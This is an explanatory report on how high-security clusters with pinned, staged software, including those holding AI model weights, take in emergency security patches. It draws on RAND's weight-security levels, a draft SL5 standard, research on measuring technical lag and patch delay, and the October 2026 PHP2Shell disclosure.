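# Emergency patching in high-security clusters that run pinned, staged software

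## How a cluster with frozen software takes in updates

A computing cluster is a group of servers that share a network and work on the same jobs. On an ordinary cluster, an administrator or a scheduled script frequently installs the newest releases from a public repository. Operators of high-security clusters often hold each program at one exact version instead, and install a newer one only after a delay and a review. Some of these clusters store the weights of frontier AI models, which are the learned numbers that encode what a model can do and most of what a thief would need to run it.

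The practice guards against poisoned updates, which are releases into which an attacker has put malicious code. But many releases are repairs, and the practice delays those too. When somebody publishes a flaw in a program that the cluster runs, the repair joins the same queue as everything else. The cluster keeps running the flawed version until the repair clears the queue or somebody decides that it can't wait. Emergency patching covers that decision and the work of installing the repair early without skipping the checks that justified the freeze.

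A zero-day is a vulnerability that attackers know of before a fix exists. A known flaw, or n-day, is one that somebody has disclosed publicly, usually under a CVE number (an entry in a shared public catalogue). A frozen cluster is about as exposed to zero-days as other systems are, since nobody has the fix yet. The freeze makes it more exposed to known flaws, because a fix exists but hasn't been brought into the cluster, while the description of the flaw, and sometimes the attack code, is public.

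### Pins, lockfiles and mirrors

Pinning a component means fixing it to one exact version, so that it changes only when someone decides to change it. For instance, a Python developer can pin a library by asking for "exactly 2.1.3" rather than "version 2.0 or later", which would let the installer pick whatever is newest that day.

Pinning only the libraries a team chose itself is not enough, because those libraries depend on others, which have dependencies of their own, and the team may never have heard of most of them. Teams therefore use a lockfile, which is generated by a tool and lists the exact version of every component in the whole tree, usually with a cryptographic hash of each. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from a file's contents. If even one byte changes, the hash no longer matches and the installer rejects the file. A lockfile with hashes can thus stop an intruder from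 swapping the file behind an existing version number, without any human review. It doesn't help if someone moves the pin to a version that was bad from the start.

An isolated cluster cannot fetch anything from a public repository, so it installs everything from an offline mirror, an internal copy of the repository that holds only what the operators have carried in. Operators can treat operating system packages, drivers and firmware the same way. In principle, someone can then name every version of every program on the cluster and the person who approved it.

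### One update, from release to production

Suppose the cluster runs version 4.2.1 of an image-decoding library, and the maintainers release 4.2.2. Details differ between organizations, but an ordinary update goes roughly like this.

Operators first have to learn that an update exists. *Securing the Software Supply Chain* (2024), guidance that the US cybersecurity agency CISA helped produce, makes the supplier responsible for notifying customers and for the integrity of its releases and updates. An open-source library may have no supplier in that sense, in which case someone on the cluster's staff watches the project's announcements.

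A staff member then downloads the release on a machine outside the perimeter that has internet access but no route into the cluster. A tool works out what else version 4.2.2 requires and writes a new lockfile. Comparing the old and new lockfiles shows the full size of the change. One small update can require a dozen others, each of which gives an attacker another opportunity.

The next checks are of the signature and the hash. A valid digital signature shows that the file was signed with the maintainers' private key, and a matching hash shows that the file didn't change on the way. Neither shows that the contents are harmless, because a malicious release will also have a valid signature if the attacker has broken into the maintainers' build system or is one of the maintainers.

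The files now cross the perimeter, on physical media or through a hardware device that passes data in only one direction, and enter quarantine. Machines in quarantine can examine the files but cannot pass them on without approval. Scanners look for malicious code and for known flaws in the new components. Reviewers read the changes between 4.2.1 and 4.2.2, if the source is available, and may run the new version in a sealed environment to see whether it opens network connections or accesses files it shouldn't need. Quality varies most at this step, because thirty changed lines are easy to read carefully but nobody reads all of a new major version of a compiler.

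After an update is approved, a careful operator has the internal build system compile the source code instead of installing the downloaded binary, so that the program on the cluster matches the code that people reviewed. The build system then signs the result with the organization's own key, and production machines accept only software signed with that key.

The next step is staging, which means holding the new version in test environments for a set time before it reaches production. The test machines should resemble the production machines closely enough to reveal crashes, slowdowns or drift in numerical results. The wait also gives others time to find problems. Thousands of other organizations are running version 4.2.2 while it is in staging, and one of them may notice if it contains something harmful.

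Finally, the operators change the pinned version, publish the package on the offline mirror and update production in batches, keeping a way to return to 4.2.1 if something breaks. Programs that loaded the old library at startup keep using it, so services have to restart, and a long training job may have to save its state and stop. Some operators also keep a "gold image", a read-only reference copy of the approved software, and regularly compare running machines with it. They have to update this image together with the machines, or the integrity check will report every patched server as tampered with.

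Computers finish the hash and signature checks in seconds. Human review and staging take most of the elapsed time, and both depend on the operator's decisions about how many reviewers to employ and how long to hold a release. The closest thing to a timetable in the AI security literature is a set of deadlines for the whole process, which comes from work on a different problem, preventing model theft.

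### The theft threat and RAND's five levels

*Securing AI Model Weights* (RAND, 2024) examines how to protect the weights of frontier models from attackers of increasing skill. Researchers at RAND, a US policy research organization, interviewed 32 experts, including government security staff and senior staff at frontier AI companies, and catalogued 38 ways to steal weights. Two matter most here. Attackers can exploit software that its owner has not updated even though a patch exists, and a company that freezes all its software is more exposed to this. They can also mount a supply chain attack through code that the organization builds into its own codebase, which is a greater risk for a company that installs every patch immediately.

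The first can happen even at experienced, careful firms. RAND's examples include the breach of LastPass, a password manager company. The breach began with a flaw in a media program on an employee's home computer. The program's vendor had patched the flaw more than two years earlier.

RAND then defined five security levels, each by the kind of attacker a system at that level should be able to thwart, and described a benchmark system for each.

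| Level | Attacker that the system should stop | Benchmark measures that bear on software updates |
|---|---|---|
| SL1 | Amateurs, and untargeted attacks | Install updates on corporate devices within two weeks of release, or a month where that is difficult or risky |
| SL2 | Most professional but opportunistic attackers | Install security updates within 7 days on personal devices and 21 days on production systems |
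| SL3 | Cybercrime syndicates and insiders | "Very frequent" updates; an inventory of all software; checks against a gold image |
| SL4 | Most standard operations by leading state-level groups | Strict list of permitted applications; verified build history for all software |
| SL5 | Most top-priority operations by the most capable states | Software only from internal developers or an extremely reliable source; a completely isolated network for the weights |

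At SL2, a machine that misses the deadline loses access. The rule also covers firmware and microcode, the low-level code inside hardware components. Each level inherits every measure from the levels below. RAND's summaries of SL4 and SL5 add restrictions on which software may run and where it may come from, but they list no faster update schedule.

These deadlines run from release to installation, so every step in the path above has to fit inside them. An operator with a 21-day deadline who keeps releases in staging for 14 days has one week left for download, review, build and rollout. A week is workable for a small fix but tight for one that also requires updating a dozen other components.

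At SL3, RAND calls for very frequent updates. It also calls for at least two people to approve any change to sensitive code, and for security staff to review every sensitive action before it happens, which RAND concedes "may introduce a significant delay". These requirements can therefore slow an urgent update when the flaw is in code close to the weights. By SL5, RAND puts security so far above availability that staff may not connect an outside device to the isolated network even to debug a critical production failure. That rule would also prevent an engineer from connecting a laptop to install an urgent fix.

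RAND judged in 2024 that nobody could yet achieve SL5, and its experts disagreed widely about the top two levels. Some thought the SL3 measures would be enough against anyone, while others thought no system would seriously hinder a top-priority operation by a major state. RAND offers the benchmarks as a guide for security teams, not a compliance standard, so the 21 days are not a requirement.

### The SL5 draft standard

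The SL5 Task Force, a non-profit group active since March 2025, is trying to turn RAND's top security level into requirements that an AI company could meet by 2028 or 2029. Its first draft, version 0.1 of *SL5 Standard for AI Security* (Thiergart, Tzfati and colleagues, 2026), assumes an adversary comparable to a thousand people with expertise years ahead of the public state of the art, working for years on a budget of up to a billion dollars. RAND considered only theft, but the draft also covers sabotage. An attacker could also use a poisoned update to corrupt research or a model in training, without sending anything out of the cluster.

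The draft is an overlay on NIST SP 800-53, the catalogue of security controls from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology. An overlay adds guidance to existing controls, each of which has a code such as CM-7(5), or fills in values that NIST left open.

The architecture has two layers. The outer layer, the SL5 Network, is air-gapped, meaning it has no connection to any external network. It may span several sites joined by encrypted links. It contains weight enclaves, which are smaller isolated zones for systems that access the weights directly, such as those that train and run the model. Each enclave stays within a single building or site, and hardware limits how fast data can leave it.

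Control CM-7(5) governs what may run in an enclave. NIST's text requires a "deny-all, permit-by-exception" policy, under which only software on an authorized list may run. NIST adds that an organization can limit the list to specific versions and check programs against hashes or signatures, which amounts to pinning. Thiergart and colleagues go further for weight enclaves. All code must be tested and cryptographically signed before it enters, and nobody may write and run code interactively inside. In the wider SL5 Network, their draft allows experiments written by AI models to run without full human review, provided they run in confined environments with few privileges.

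The AI chips, or accelerators, must accept only firmware that the manufacturer has signed, and they check the signature with keys the manufacturer built into the hardware. This stops an intruder who has taken over the host computer from installing their own firmware. It also means that an operator who learns of a firmware flaw has to wait for the manufacturer to fix it, even in an emergency.

Under AC-4, all external data must first go to a "staging area" that is physically separate from internal systems, and it may move on only after screening. (This staging area serves as the quarantine described above, not as the test machines where a new version sits out its waiting period.) The draft guidance lists code and configuration files among the data to screen, so its wording covers software releases. But these controls are mainly meant to stop attacks on AI models, such as poisoned training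 data, and they set no waiting period.

They write that detecting adversarial content remains an open research problem and that the best available defences are insufficient against sophisticated attackers. In the SL5 Task Force's *Security Architecture Overview*, external data stays isolated until it completes both automated detection and human review. The detailed control, however, requires people to review only what the detector has flagged or could not process, and the organization may choose to check only a sample of that. A poisoned release that the detector passes could therefore clear AC-4 without any human reading it, and the testing and signing under CM-7(5) would have to catch it. A sensible provision partly reduces this risk by requiring organizations to record which version of the detector screened which data, so that they can rescan old material when detection improves.

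The SL5 Task Force's draft *SL5 Standard for AI Security* (2026) has almost no guidance of its own on repairing flaws. The relevant NIST control is SI-2, flaw remediation, which is in NIST's low, moderate and high baselines. As reproduced in Open Security Architecture's *SI-02 Flaw Remediation*, it requires an organization to find and correct flaws, test updates for effectiveness and side effects before installing them, install security-relevant updates within a period it sets for itself, and do all this within its normal change management. Version 0.1 of the SL5 standard adds no guidance to SI-2. The web edition, which the group updated on 4 June 2026, is still version 0.1, with 43 controls in ten families, the same number as in March.

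The draft deliberately leaves this for later. Thiergart and colleagues describe it as partial and limit it to measures that take years to prepare, such as buildings and chips. The complete standard is to build on Impact Level 6, a US Defense Department baseline for cloud systems that handle classified data, and later revisions will map the two together. An operator would presumably inherit SI-2 that way. But SI-2 leaves the number of days blank, so someone has to set it for a cluster where every change must be tested, signed and carried across an air gap.

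There is also a case for dealing with emergency patching sooner. An organization can set a patching deadline in an afternoon, but it needs longer to put in place what it takes to meet one: a second set of accelerators for testing, an internal build system that can compile the whole software stack, and enough cleared reviewers to call some in at the weekend. These look much like the long-lead items that version 0.1 is meant to identify.

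Outsiders can't easily tell how much of this regime AI companies already run, because the labs do not state their security levels publicly. In *Security*, a talk published by the research group FAR.AI, the speaker gave a personal estimate that most frontier labs were just finishing SL2 and moving into SL3, with some perhaps starting on parts of SL4. If that is about right, the enclave with its tested and signed code is mostly a plan, and RAND's 21-day rule is closer to the standard these companies are working from. Meanwhile, NIST has released an initial draft of security recommendations for AI data centers in response to a White House call for technical standards for high-security sites, according to the law firm Wiley's *A New Framework for AI Data Center Security* (2026).

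### The same delay holds back both

Suppose the cluster keeps every release of the image library in staging for 14 days. If version 4.2.2 is poisoned and another user finds the malicious code on day 5, the operators delete the file and lose nothing. But if version 4.2.2 fixes a serious flaw, attackers can find that flaw by comparing the release with 4.2.1, and the cluster keeps running the vulnerable version for those 14 days, plus the time needed for review and rollout. The operators can't reliably tell on day 0 whether a release is poisoned or an urgent fix. It may even be both, since an attacker who wants quick adoption has good reason to label a poisoned release as an urgent security fix.

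RAND counted 21 high-severity vulnerabilities over nine years in OpenSSL, the library that encrypts much of the internet's traffic. That is more than two a year in a single component. A cluster that used the full 21 days each time would have spent up to 441 days of those nine years with a serious, public flaw in that library.

An air gap changes these odds without removing the problem. An outsider can't directly send an attack to a machine that has no connection, but RAND's list of attack routes includes reaching into air-gapped networks, and an insider is already past the gap. RAND also insists that effort against one category of attack does not make up for a hole in another, so an operator can't offset the risk of old software by vetting new software more strictly. A longer wait gives the rest of the world more time to expose a poisoned release. Tools can enforce the wait automatically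 with a cooldown, a rule that refuses any release younger than a set number of days. But waiting also widens technical lag, the gap between the version installed and the version one would ideally run. No single waiting period suits both a poisoned release and an urgent repair, so a cluster that freezes its software also needs a way to make exceptions.

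## Measuring how far pinned software falls behind

Gonzalez-Barahona and colleagues coined the term "technical lag" in 2017 for the gap between installed and ideal software. They wanted to distinguish it from technical debt, which programmers take on when they choose a shortcut. *Technical Lag as Latent Technical Debt* (Panter and Eisty, 2026) describes lag as accumulating passively, as the installed version stays the same while its maintainers keep releasing new ones. Operators of a pinned cluster choose to run behind as a matter of policy, and they need to know how far behind they are.

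### Choosing an ideal and a distance

To measure lag, someone has to pick an ideal version of each package, decide how to measure its distance from the installed version, and decide how to combine the distances. In symbols:

$$\text{TechLag}(D,S)=\underset{i\in C}{\text{Agg}}\ \text{Lag}(d_i,s_i)$$

Here C is the set of components, d_i is the installed version of component i, and s_i is its ideal version. Lag measures the distance between the two versions, and Agg combines these distances, usually by adding them. Lag is zero when the installed version is at least as new as the ideal, so a component that is ahead cannot offset one that is behind.

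The formula doesn't specify which version is ideal, and people disagree about it. CHAOSS, an open-source project that develops metrics for software communities, presented a small online survey on which version of a library is best to depend on. The 17 respondents could give more than one answer. Fourteen chose the most stable version, nine the latest and only five the most secure.

A cluster that holds every release in staging for 14 days could measure its lag against the newest release that is at least 14 days old. If it followed its own rules, its lag would be close to zero, and a long lag would indicate neglect. Measured against the newest release of all, the same cluster would nearly always look late. Panter and Eisty identify a gap in the research: current metrics can't distinguish a deliberate protective delay from neglect, and none estimates when a release has become safe to adopt.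 For measuring exposure to known flaws, though, the newest release is the right comparison, because attackers can exploit a flaw while its fix is still in staging.

Engineers can measure how far pinned software has fallen behind as a length of time, a number of releases or a number of unfixed flaws. In an invented example, an engineer checks a lockfile with four packages on 1 June 2026 and treats each package's newest release as the ideal version.

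| Package | Installed version | Newest version | Days between the two | Releases missed | Known flaws fixed since |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Image decoder | 4.2.1 (12 May 2026) | 4.2.2 (26 May 2026) | 14 | 1 | 3 |
| HTTP client | 3.4.0 (2 March 2026) | 3.9.2 (20 May 2026) | 79 | 14 | 1 |
| Logging library | 2.10.0 (1 September 2025) | 2.13.0 (1 April 2026) | 212 | 4 | 2 |
| Compression library | 1.8.0 (1 June 2023) | 1.9.1 (25 May 2026) | 1,089 | 2 | 0 |

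The compression library is the worst of the four by time, the HTTP client by releases, and the image decoder by flaws, so the choice of measure affects which one the engineer updates first. Updating the compression library would remove 78% of the total lag in days but no flaws, while updating the image decoder would remove 1% of the lag in days and half of the flaws.

Even the time column can overstate the delay. It shows 1,089 days for the compression library, but the library's maintainers released nothing for almost three years. If version 1.9.0 came out on 18 May, the cluster had been missing an update for only 14 days. Panter and Eisty call this shorter figure opportunity lag, the time during which an update was available and nobody installed it. Counts of releases have a similar weakness, because they depend on how often the maintainers publish.

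Researchers have mostly used the measures that are easiest to compute. Of the 18 studies that Panter and Eisty reviewed, ten measured lag in time, six counted versions, and fewer counted flaws. *MALTA* (2026), a paper on abandoned software, cites an analysis of Docker images that used several measures of lag together and found that they complement each other.

### Docker images in 2018

A Docker image bundles an application with the system libraries it needs. Its packages stay frozen after it is built, so it is a small-scale version of a pinned cluster. Zerouali, Mens and colleagues examined 7,380 images based on Debian, a widely used Linux distribution, in *On The Relation Between Outdated Docker Containers, Severity Vulnerabilities and Bugs* (2018). They listed the packages in each image, matched them against daily snapshots of Debian's archive, and looked up their known flaws in Debian's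 security tracker.

The lag was small. In the median image, 82% of packages were the latest version available within the same Debian release, and the rest were typically one or two versions behind. Among images updated in 2018, the median was 98%.

The median image contained 601 known flaws, and every image had some of high severity. Even the least affected image based on Debian 8, the oldest release in the sample, had 155 flaws. Images with more outdated packages tended to have more flaws, but the correlation was only moderate to moderately strong, partly because nearly half of the flaws had no fix and updating would not have removed them. When Debian did fix a high-severity flaw, the median time from bug report to fix was 2.1 months.

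The raw counts overstate the danger, since about a fifth of the flaws were labeled "unimportant", and these Debian releases are now old. But the result still matters for a cluster because it separates the wait for a fix, which depends on the maintainers, from the wait to install it, which an operator can shorten. A measure of lag doesn't include the wait for a fix.

### Stale pins in Maven

Maven, a package system for Java, pins dependencies by default. In *On the Freshness of Pinned Dependencies in Maven*, Vikram, Agarwal and Padhye (2025) studied how often developers let those pinned versions become outdated. They examined every project in a snapshot from 22 May 2023 that depended on one of the 500 libraries with the most users.

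Vikram and colleagues call a pin stale if a newer compatible version was already out when the project published its own release. They count a version as compatible if it has the same major number under semantic versioning, a convention in which versions have the form major.minor.patch and a change in the major number signals breaking changes. Upgrading to a compatible version should, in principle, have been painless.

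Of 244,819 projects that used one of the libraries directly, 61% had at least one stale pin. The median stale version was 370 days and seven releases out of date. Indirect dependencies, which a project gets through its other dependencies, were older, at 427 days and nine releases. This is unsurprising, because a developer has to override someone else's choice to change an indirect version.

The paper's abstract also says that 10% of upgrades would have reduced vulnerabilities. This percentage has a different denominator. It counts distinct upgrades, each a pair of one old version and one newer version of the same library, and not projects. If ten thousand projects all pinned the same old release, they would add one upgrade to the count. There were 46,365 distinct upgrades from direct stale pins:

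| Effect of the upgrade on known flaws | Upgrades | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Fewer flaws | 4,576 | 9.9% |
| No change | 40,462 | 87.2% |
| More flaws | 1,327 | 2.9% |

Upgrading would have helped 22,447 projects, about 15% of those with a stale direct pin. So most stale pins did no known harm to security, and a cluster operator who reviews every release will spend most of that effort on releases that fix no known flaw. But the operator can't safely skip those releases on that basis. Vikram and colleagues deliberately used an old snapshot, so that researchers had about a year and a half to discover flaws in it. Some of the flaws they counted were therefore unknown when the project shipped. Likewise, a version with no known flaws when a cluster operator approves it may have known flaws a year later.

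The researchers also measured some of the risk of upgrading. They built a tool that runs other projects' published tests against the old and new versions of a library. They found no such tests for 3,268 of the 4,576 helpful upgrades. Of the 1,308 they could check, 458 scored zero, which means that a test that passed on the old version failed on the new one. More than a third of the testable security upgrades therefore came with a warning, although all of them were supposed to be compatible. This gives operators some reason to insist on staging even small fixes.

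### Pinned and floating versions

The alternative to a pin is a floating rule, which lets the installer choose the newest version within a range. In *Which Is Better For Reducing Outdated and Vulnerable Dependencies* (2025), Rahman, Marley and colleagues compared pinning and floating in npm, PyPI and Cargo, the package systems for JavaScript, Python and Rust. They reconstructed which version each rule would have selected at each point in the past, and marked the periods when that version was outdated or had a known flaw with an available fix.

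Pins made up 29% of dependency declarations in PyPI but accounted for 66% of the time that packages spent with vulnerable dependencies. The difference was smaller in npm, where pins made up 30% of declarations and accounted for 38% of the vulnerable time. Few developers pin in Cargo, and pins accounted for almost none of the vulnerable time there.

They then estimated hazard ratios using the 1,000 highest-rated packages from each system. A hazard ratio compares how likely an event is at any given moment under two conditions. Here the event is a dependency becoming outdated or vulnerable, and the baseline is pinning, so a ratio of 0.5 means half the risk of a pinned dependency.

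| Version rule | Risk of becoming outdated | Risk of becoming vulnerable |
|---|---|---|
| Pin to one version | 1 | 1 |
| Accept new patch releases | 0.75 | 1.48 |
| Accept new minor and patch releases | 0.44 | 0.57 |
| Accept any newer release | 0.01 | Too few cases to estimate |
| Fixed range with upper and lower limit | 0.62 | 2.69 |

In the outdatedness column, looser rules keep dependencies fresher, as expected. In the vulnerability column, however, a rule that accepts patch releases unexpectedly did worse than a pin. Rahman and colleagues attribute this to maintainers who fix only one major version. They found 4,219 CVEs that affected several major versions but were fixed in only one. For example, a flaw in the npm package dset affected everything up to 3.1.1, and the maintainers fixed it in 3.1.2 but not in the 0, 1 or 2 series, so somebody who accepts only patches to version 2 will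 never get the fix.

That explains why a narrow floating rule may be no better than a pin, but not why it would be worse. A floating rule that starts from the same version as a pin should nearly always select the same release or a later one. More likely, the developers who choose pins differ from those who choose floating rules, and may watch their dependencies more closely and move the pins by hand. The study also recorded about 5.4 million changes in which a dependency switched between outdated and current or between vulnerable and fixed. Of these, 98% happened when a developer edited the version but kept the same type of rule, which fits this explanation. The ratios therefore reflect habits in three open-source communities and don't isolate the effect of the rule itself. They also measure how soon a dependency becomes vulnerable, while a cluster operator cares at least as much about how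 long it stays vulnerable.

Rahman and colleagues advise developers to avoid pins and use floating rules with a lockfile. This differs from the practice of a high-security cluster mostly in vocabulary. They use "pinning" to mean the version rule a developer writes, and the lockfile still fixes the exact version of everything the installer fetches. A cluster can therefore follow the advice and install nothing new until someone approves a new lockfile. The floating rule only makes the next candidate lockfile easier to generate, because the tool can propose new versions without anyone editing each line.

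### Time to update and time to remediate

A lag figure describes one moment, so an operator who updated everything last night will look excellent today even if they then do nothing for a year. Mean time to update (MTTU) and mean time to remediate (MTTR) cover a period of time. MTTU measures how long a package used outdated dependencies, and MTTR measures how long it used dependencies with a flaw that already had a fix.

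Subtracting the date of a dependency version from the date of the package release that uses it is not a workable way to measure how far the package has fallen behind. Rahman, Zahan and colleagues (2024) show why in *Characterizing Dependency Update Practice Of NPM, PyPI and Cargo Packages*, using the web framework Express as an example. Express 2.4.3, from July 2011, accepts any version of a library called qs from 0.0.6 upwards. An installer running in 2024 would select a version of qs from May 2024, so the subtraction gives minus 4,680 days. Across many packages, such negative values cancel positive ones and pull the average towards zero.

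The solution was to split the history of each dependency into intervals, with a new interval whenever the package or the dependency published a release. Nothing changes within an interval, so it is either outdated or not. Rahman, Paramitha and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Stars*, give the current formula, which amounts to this:

$$\text{MTTU}=\frac{T_1+T_2+\dots+T_n}{n}$$

Here n is the number of direct dependencies, and each T is the total time, in days, that one dependency was outdated. For MTTR, each T is the total time that the selected version had a known flaw and a fix was already out.

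Despite its name, this is the total number of outdated days per dependency, not the average delay per update, so it grows with the length of the record. A package that takes a week over each of fifty updates has the same time to update as one that ignored a single update for 350 days. *Beyond Stars* also offers a version that averages the interval lengths, giving recent intervals more weight. Security teams often use "MTTR" for the average time from finding a problem to fixing it, so anyone comparing two such figures should check the definition first.

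The 2024 study applied the unweighted method to data on 2.9 million packages, under the names "time out of date" and "post-fix exposure time". These are the mean values in days:

| Package system | Outdated dependencies | Vulnerable dependencies with a fix available |
|---|---|---|
| PyPI | 109 | 436 |
| Cargo | 166 | 366 |
| npm | 582 | 962 |

The two columns cover different groups of packages. The first, for time spent outdated, covers about 1.4 million npm packages, including some that were never outdated. The second, for time spent vulnerable, seems to include only the roughly 219,000 npm packages with at least some exposure, so it measures how bad the problem was for affected packages, not how common it was. This difference would explain why packages appear to stay vulnerable for longer than they stay outdated, which is impossible for any one package because a dependency that has missed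 a fix is outdated by definition.

Suppose the cluster has run each installed version in the lockfile above since the day of its release, and that each flaw became public on the day the package's newest release fixed it. By 1 June, the image decoder has been vulnerable for 6 days, the HTTP client for 12, the logging library for 61 and the compression library for 0. If all four are direct dependencies, the mean time to remediate is just under 20 days.

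This calculation treats a day with three flaws the same as a day with one. Flaw-days correct for that by multiplying the number of known flaws by the days each one stays unfixed. The image decoder has 18 flaw-days, the HTTP client 12 and the logging library 122. The logging library looks worst by this measure because its two flaws have gone unfixed for two months, although it did not come first in any column of the earlier table.

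*Beyond Stars* lists further limits. The formula covers only direct dependencies, although the Maven figures suggest that indirect ones are older. It also leaves out flaws that were never fixed, because a developer can't install a fix that doesn't exist. That is fair when judging developers, but an unfixed flaw still exposes a cluster. This report's exposure window starts at disclosure, so if the fix comes two weeks later, MTTR leaves out those two weeks.

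Because many packages have few recorded flaws, some researchers use time to update as a stand-in for time to remediate. The 2024 study found correlations between the two of 0.7 on two standard measures and 0.5 on a third. *Assumptions to Evidence* (2025), which examined security practices in npm, relied on those correlations and on the argument that security updates are a subset of all updates. The stand-in works for developers who treat all updates alike, but it would fail for a cluster with a good emergency procedure, which might leave ordinary updates for months and install urgent fixes in two days.

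### Software that companies run

Most of these figures describe the dependencies that open-source developers declared in their projects, which may not match what anyone has installed. *State of DevSecOps* (2026), from the monitoring software vendor Datadog, comes closer to production use because it examined the libraries active in customers' services in January 2026. The median dependency was 278 days behind, up from 215 a year earlier. For Java, the median was 492 days.

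The report is not quite clear about which dates it compares. The main text says that dependencies are 278 days behind their "latest major version", while the methodology refers to the latest update within the current major version. The two dates can be far apart when a library's maintainers still release fixes for older major versions. The sample consists of Datadog customers who use its tool for finding vulnerable libraries, and they may pay more attention to the problem than most companies do.

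Datadog also grouped services by how often their owners deploy them. Dependencies were a median of 172 days behind in services deployed daily and 295 days behind in those deployed less than once a month. A pinned cluster is more like the second group. The comparison doesn't prove that rare deployment causes the lag, since neglect probably reduces both deployments and updates.

Although these organizations were slow to update, half of them had used some library version within a day of its publication. An organization that is nine months behind on most of its libraries can still install a malicious update on the day it is released if nothing delays updates to the others.

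### Flaws that the counts get wrong

A count of known flaws usually comes from matching package names and versions against a database, which can produce both false positives and false negatives.

A package may contain a flaw in code that never runs. In *Vuln4Real*, Pashchenko, Plate and colleagues studied the 500 open-source Java libraries that the software company SAP used most, covering 25,767 versions. Many dependencies are used only for building or testing and never reach production. After removing these and correcting some other errors, the researchers found that 27% of the alerts about direct dependencies and 21% of those about indirect ones concerned flaws that could not be exploited. Database entries also cause false alerts when they name a whole project although only one of its libraries has the flaw.

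Some packages reach production even though the application doesn't need them. According to earlier research cited in *Out of Sight, Still at Risk* (2025), 57% of indirect dependencies in Maven are bloat of this kind, compared with 2% of direct ones. Lag and flaw counts include these unneeded packages. Testing whether an attacker can reach the flawed code is part of deciding which flaws to fix first.

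Version numbers can also exaggerate the lag of distribution packages. Debian's stable releases keep an old version of a program and add security fixes to it, a practice called backporting. Zerouali and colleagues found that 80% of the up-to-date package versions in images based on Debian 9 were older than Debian 9, yet had the latest fix available for that release. Such a package may be years behind the original project's newest version while being current with Debian's own archive. A scanner that checks only the original project's version numbers will report flaws that Debian has already fixed.

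Errors that understate the risk are more dangerous than errors that overstate it. Pashchenko and colleagues mention spring-dao, a Java library whose development had stopped. It has a known flaw and no fixed version, so a cluster that runs the last release has no lag but stays vulnerable permanently. Maintainers also fix some flaws without announcing them, as the 2024 study of npm, PyPI and Cargo points out, so no count includes those flaws.

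Lag is hardest to measure for closed drivers and firmware, and an AI cluster depends on both. If the manufacturer publishes dated releases, the operator can usually work out how many days or releases behind a driver is. But the operator's count of unfixed flaws depends on what the manufacturer chooses to disclose, and outsiders can't check it by comparing the source code of two versions, so a driver with no known flaws may still have undisclosed ones. None of the 18 studies that Panter and Eisty reviewed focuses on closed drivers or firmware.

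### Isolated clusters

None of those 18 studies measures an air-gapped network, an industrial control system or a supercomputer either. They cover public package systems, Linux distributions, Docker images, Android apps and GitHub projects. Older work on commercial software comes closest to covering private sites. *Measuring dependency freshness in software systems* (Cox, 2014) analysed systems from industry and proposed a rating for how current each one was. Zerouali and colleagues report that a later study by Cox and others covered 75 systems and found security issues four times as often in those with outdated dependencies. These were business systems, and nothing suggests that they were isolated. Datadog's sample is even less likely to include isolated clusters, since a machine with no outside connection can't report to a monitoring company.

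An isolated cluster could do better or worse than these figures. Carrying each update across an air gap takes work, which encourages operators to batch updates. But such a cluster should have a full inventory and dedicated maintenance staff, and many of the open-source projects in these studies have neither. A cluster that met RAND's benchmark of 21 days for security updates on production systems would be unusual, with ordinary packages perhaps a year old but almost no fixable flaws older than three weeks. It would look worse than the average company by Datadog's measure but probably much better by flaw-days.

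Operators can measure this lag for their own cluster. The offline mirror should record when each version arrived and when production began to use it, and public databases give the dates of disclosures and fixes. An engineer can use these dates to calculate flaw-days for every package, including indirect dependencies, and to separate the days spent waiting for a fix from those spent in review, staging and rollout. This calculation treats every flaw as equally serious, as Rahman and colleagues did in their 2025 comparison, so a team that can bring only a few fixes across the air gap in a given week also needs a way to rank them.

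## Deciding which flaws cannot wait

Attackers use only a small share of disclosed flaws. Jay Jacobs and colleagues looked at about 76,000 flaws published between 2009 and 2018 and found evidence of attacks on about 5.5% of them. The true share is probably higher, since nobody sees every attack, but a team that treated every flaw as an emergency would still spend most of its effort on flaws that attackers never used.

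When attackers exploit a flaw, they often do so soon after its patch is released. Mandiant, a security company owned by Google, estimated that the average gap between a flaw's patch and its exploitation fell from 63 days in 2018 and 2019 to five days in 2023. At those averages, a cluster that holds releases in staging for 14 days would have installed a patch well before attacks began in the earlier period, but by 2023 the attacks would have come first.

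Most organizations are slower than that. According to Verizon's 2026 breach report, organizations fully fixed only 26% of the flaws in CISA's KEV catalog, which lists vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited. The figure was 38% a year earlier, according to the security company Tenable. Verizon puts the median time to a full fix at 43 days, which presumably covers only the flaws that were fully fixed.

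AI affects both how fast attackers exploit flaws and how many flaws are found. CISA (2026) warned when it announced new patching rules in June that attackers' use of AI may further shorten the time between a patch and the first attack. In *How CISA's BOD 26-04 changes vulnerability prioritization*, DePinto and Wang claim that attackers can now weaponize flaws in hours or minutes, when this once took weeks or months. However, they market security products for Datadog and give no data to support the claim. AI models also find flaws, which adds to the team's queue. If disclosures doubled while the number of exploited flaws rose by half, the exploited share would drop from 5.5% to about 4%, but the team would have 50% more real emergencies to handle.

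### The PHP flaws of October 2026

PHP, a programming language, runs on more than 70% of websites by some estimates. In October 2026 its maintainers fixed two flaws that together let an attacker run code on a web server without logging in. CVE-2026-109618 corrupts the program's memory, and CVE-2026-109619 involves stale internal data about a request. Security staff call the pair PHP2Shell.

Greig (2026) reported in *PHP says AI review of critical bugs first sparked alarm in August* that PHP's maintainers had known about the memory flaw since an outside audit in 2024. They knew of no way to use it to run code and worried that a fix would break third-party extensions, so work stalled and restarted for months. The flaws got serious attention only in August 2026, after AI companies reviewed the code.

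The PHP team planned to publish the fixes at 14:00 UTC on 21 October and kept the details under embargo until then. *Critical PHP Vulnerabilities Leaked Ahead of Scheduled Security Patch* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the details leaked a day early. *PHP Foundation Says Chainguard Broke Security Embargo Ahead of Emergency Patches* (Gooding, 2026) describes how the Foundation blamed Chainguard, a company that sells hardened container images. In Tom's Hardware's *Devastated forum user who accidentally broke the PHP news embargo comes clean*, a forum user says they broke the embargo without knowing of any restriction.

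At least one attacker acted even earlier, sending an exploit attempt on 17 October to one of Amazon's honeypots, which are decoy servers that record attacks. Amazon doesn't know how the attacker got the details, or whether the attempt would have worked on a real system. Tsai's *PHP2Shell* (2026) collects Amazon's account along with other first-hand posts. OffSeq's *PHP2Shell in the wild* (2026) reports a first suspicious request about sixteen hours before the fix. On 21 October, Amazon identified several proof-of-concept exploits, the earliest at around 02:00 UTC, twelve hours before the planned release.

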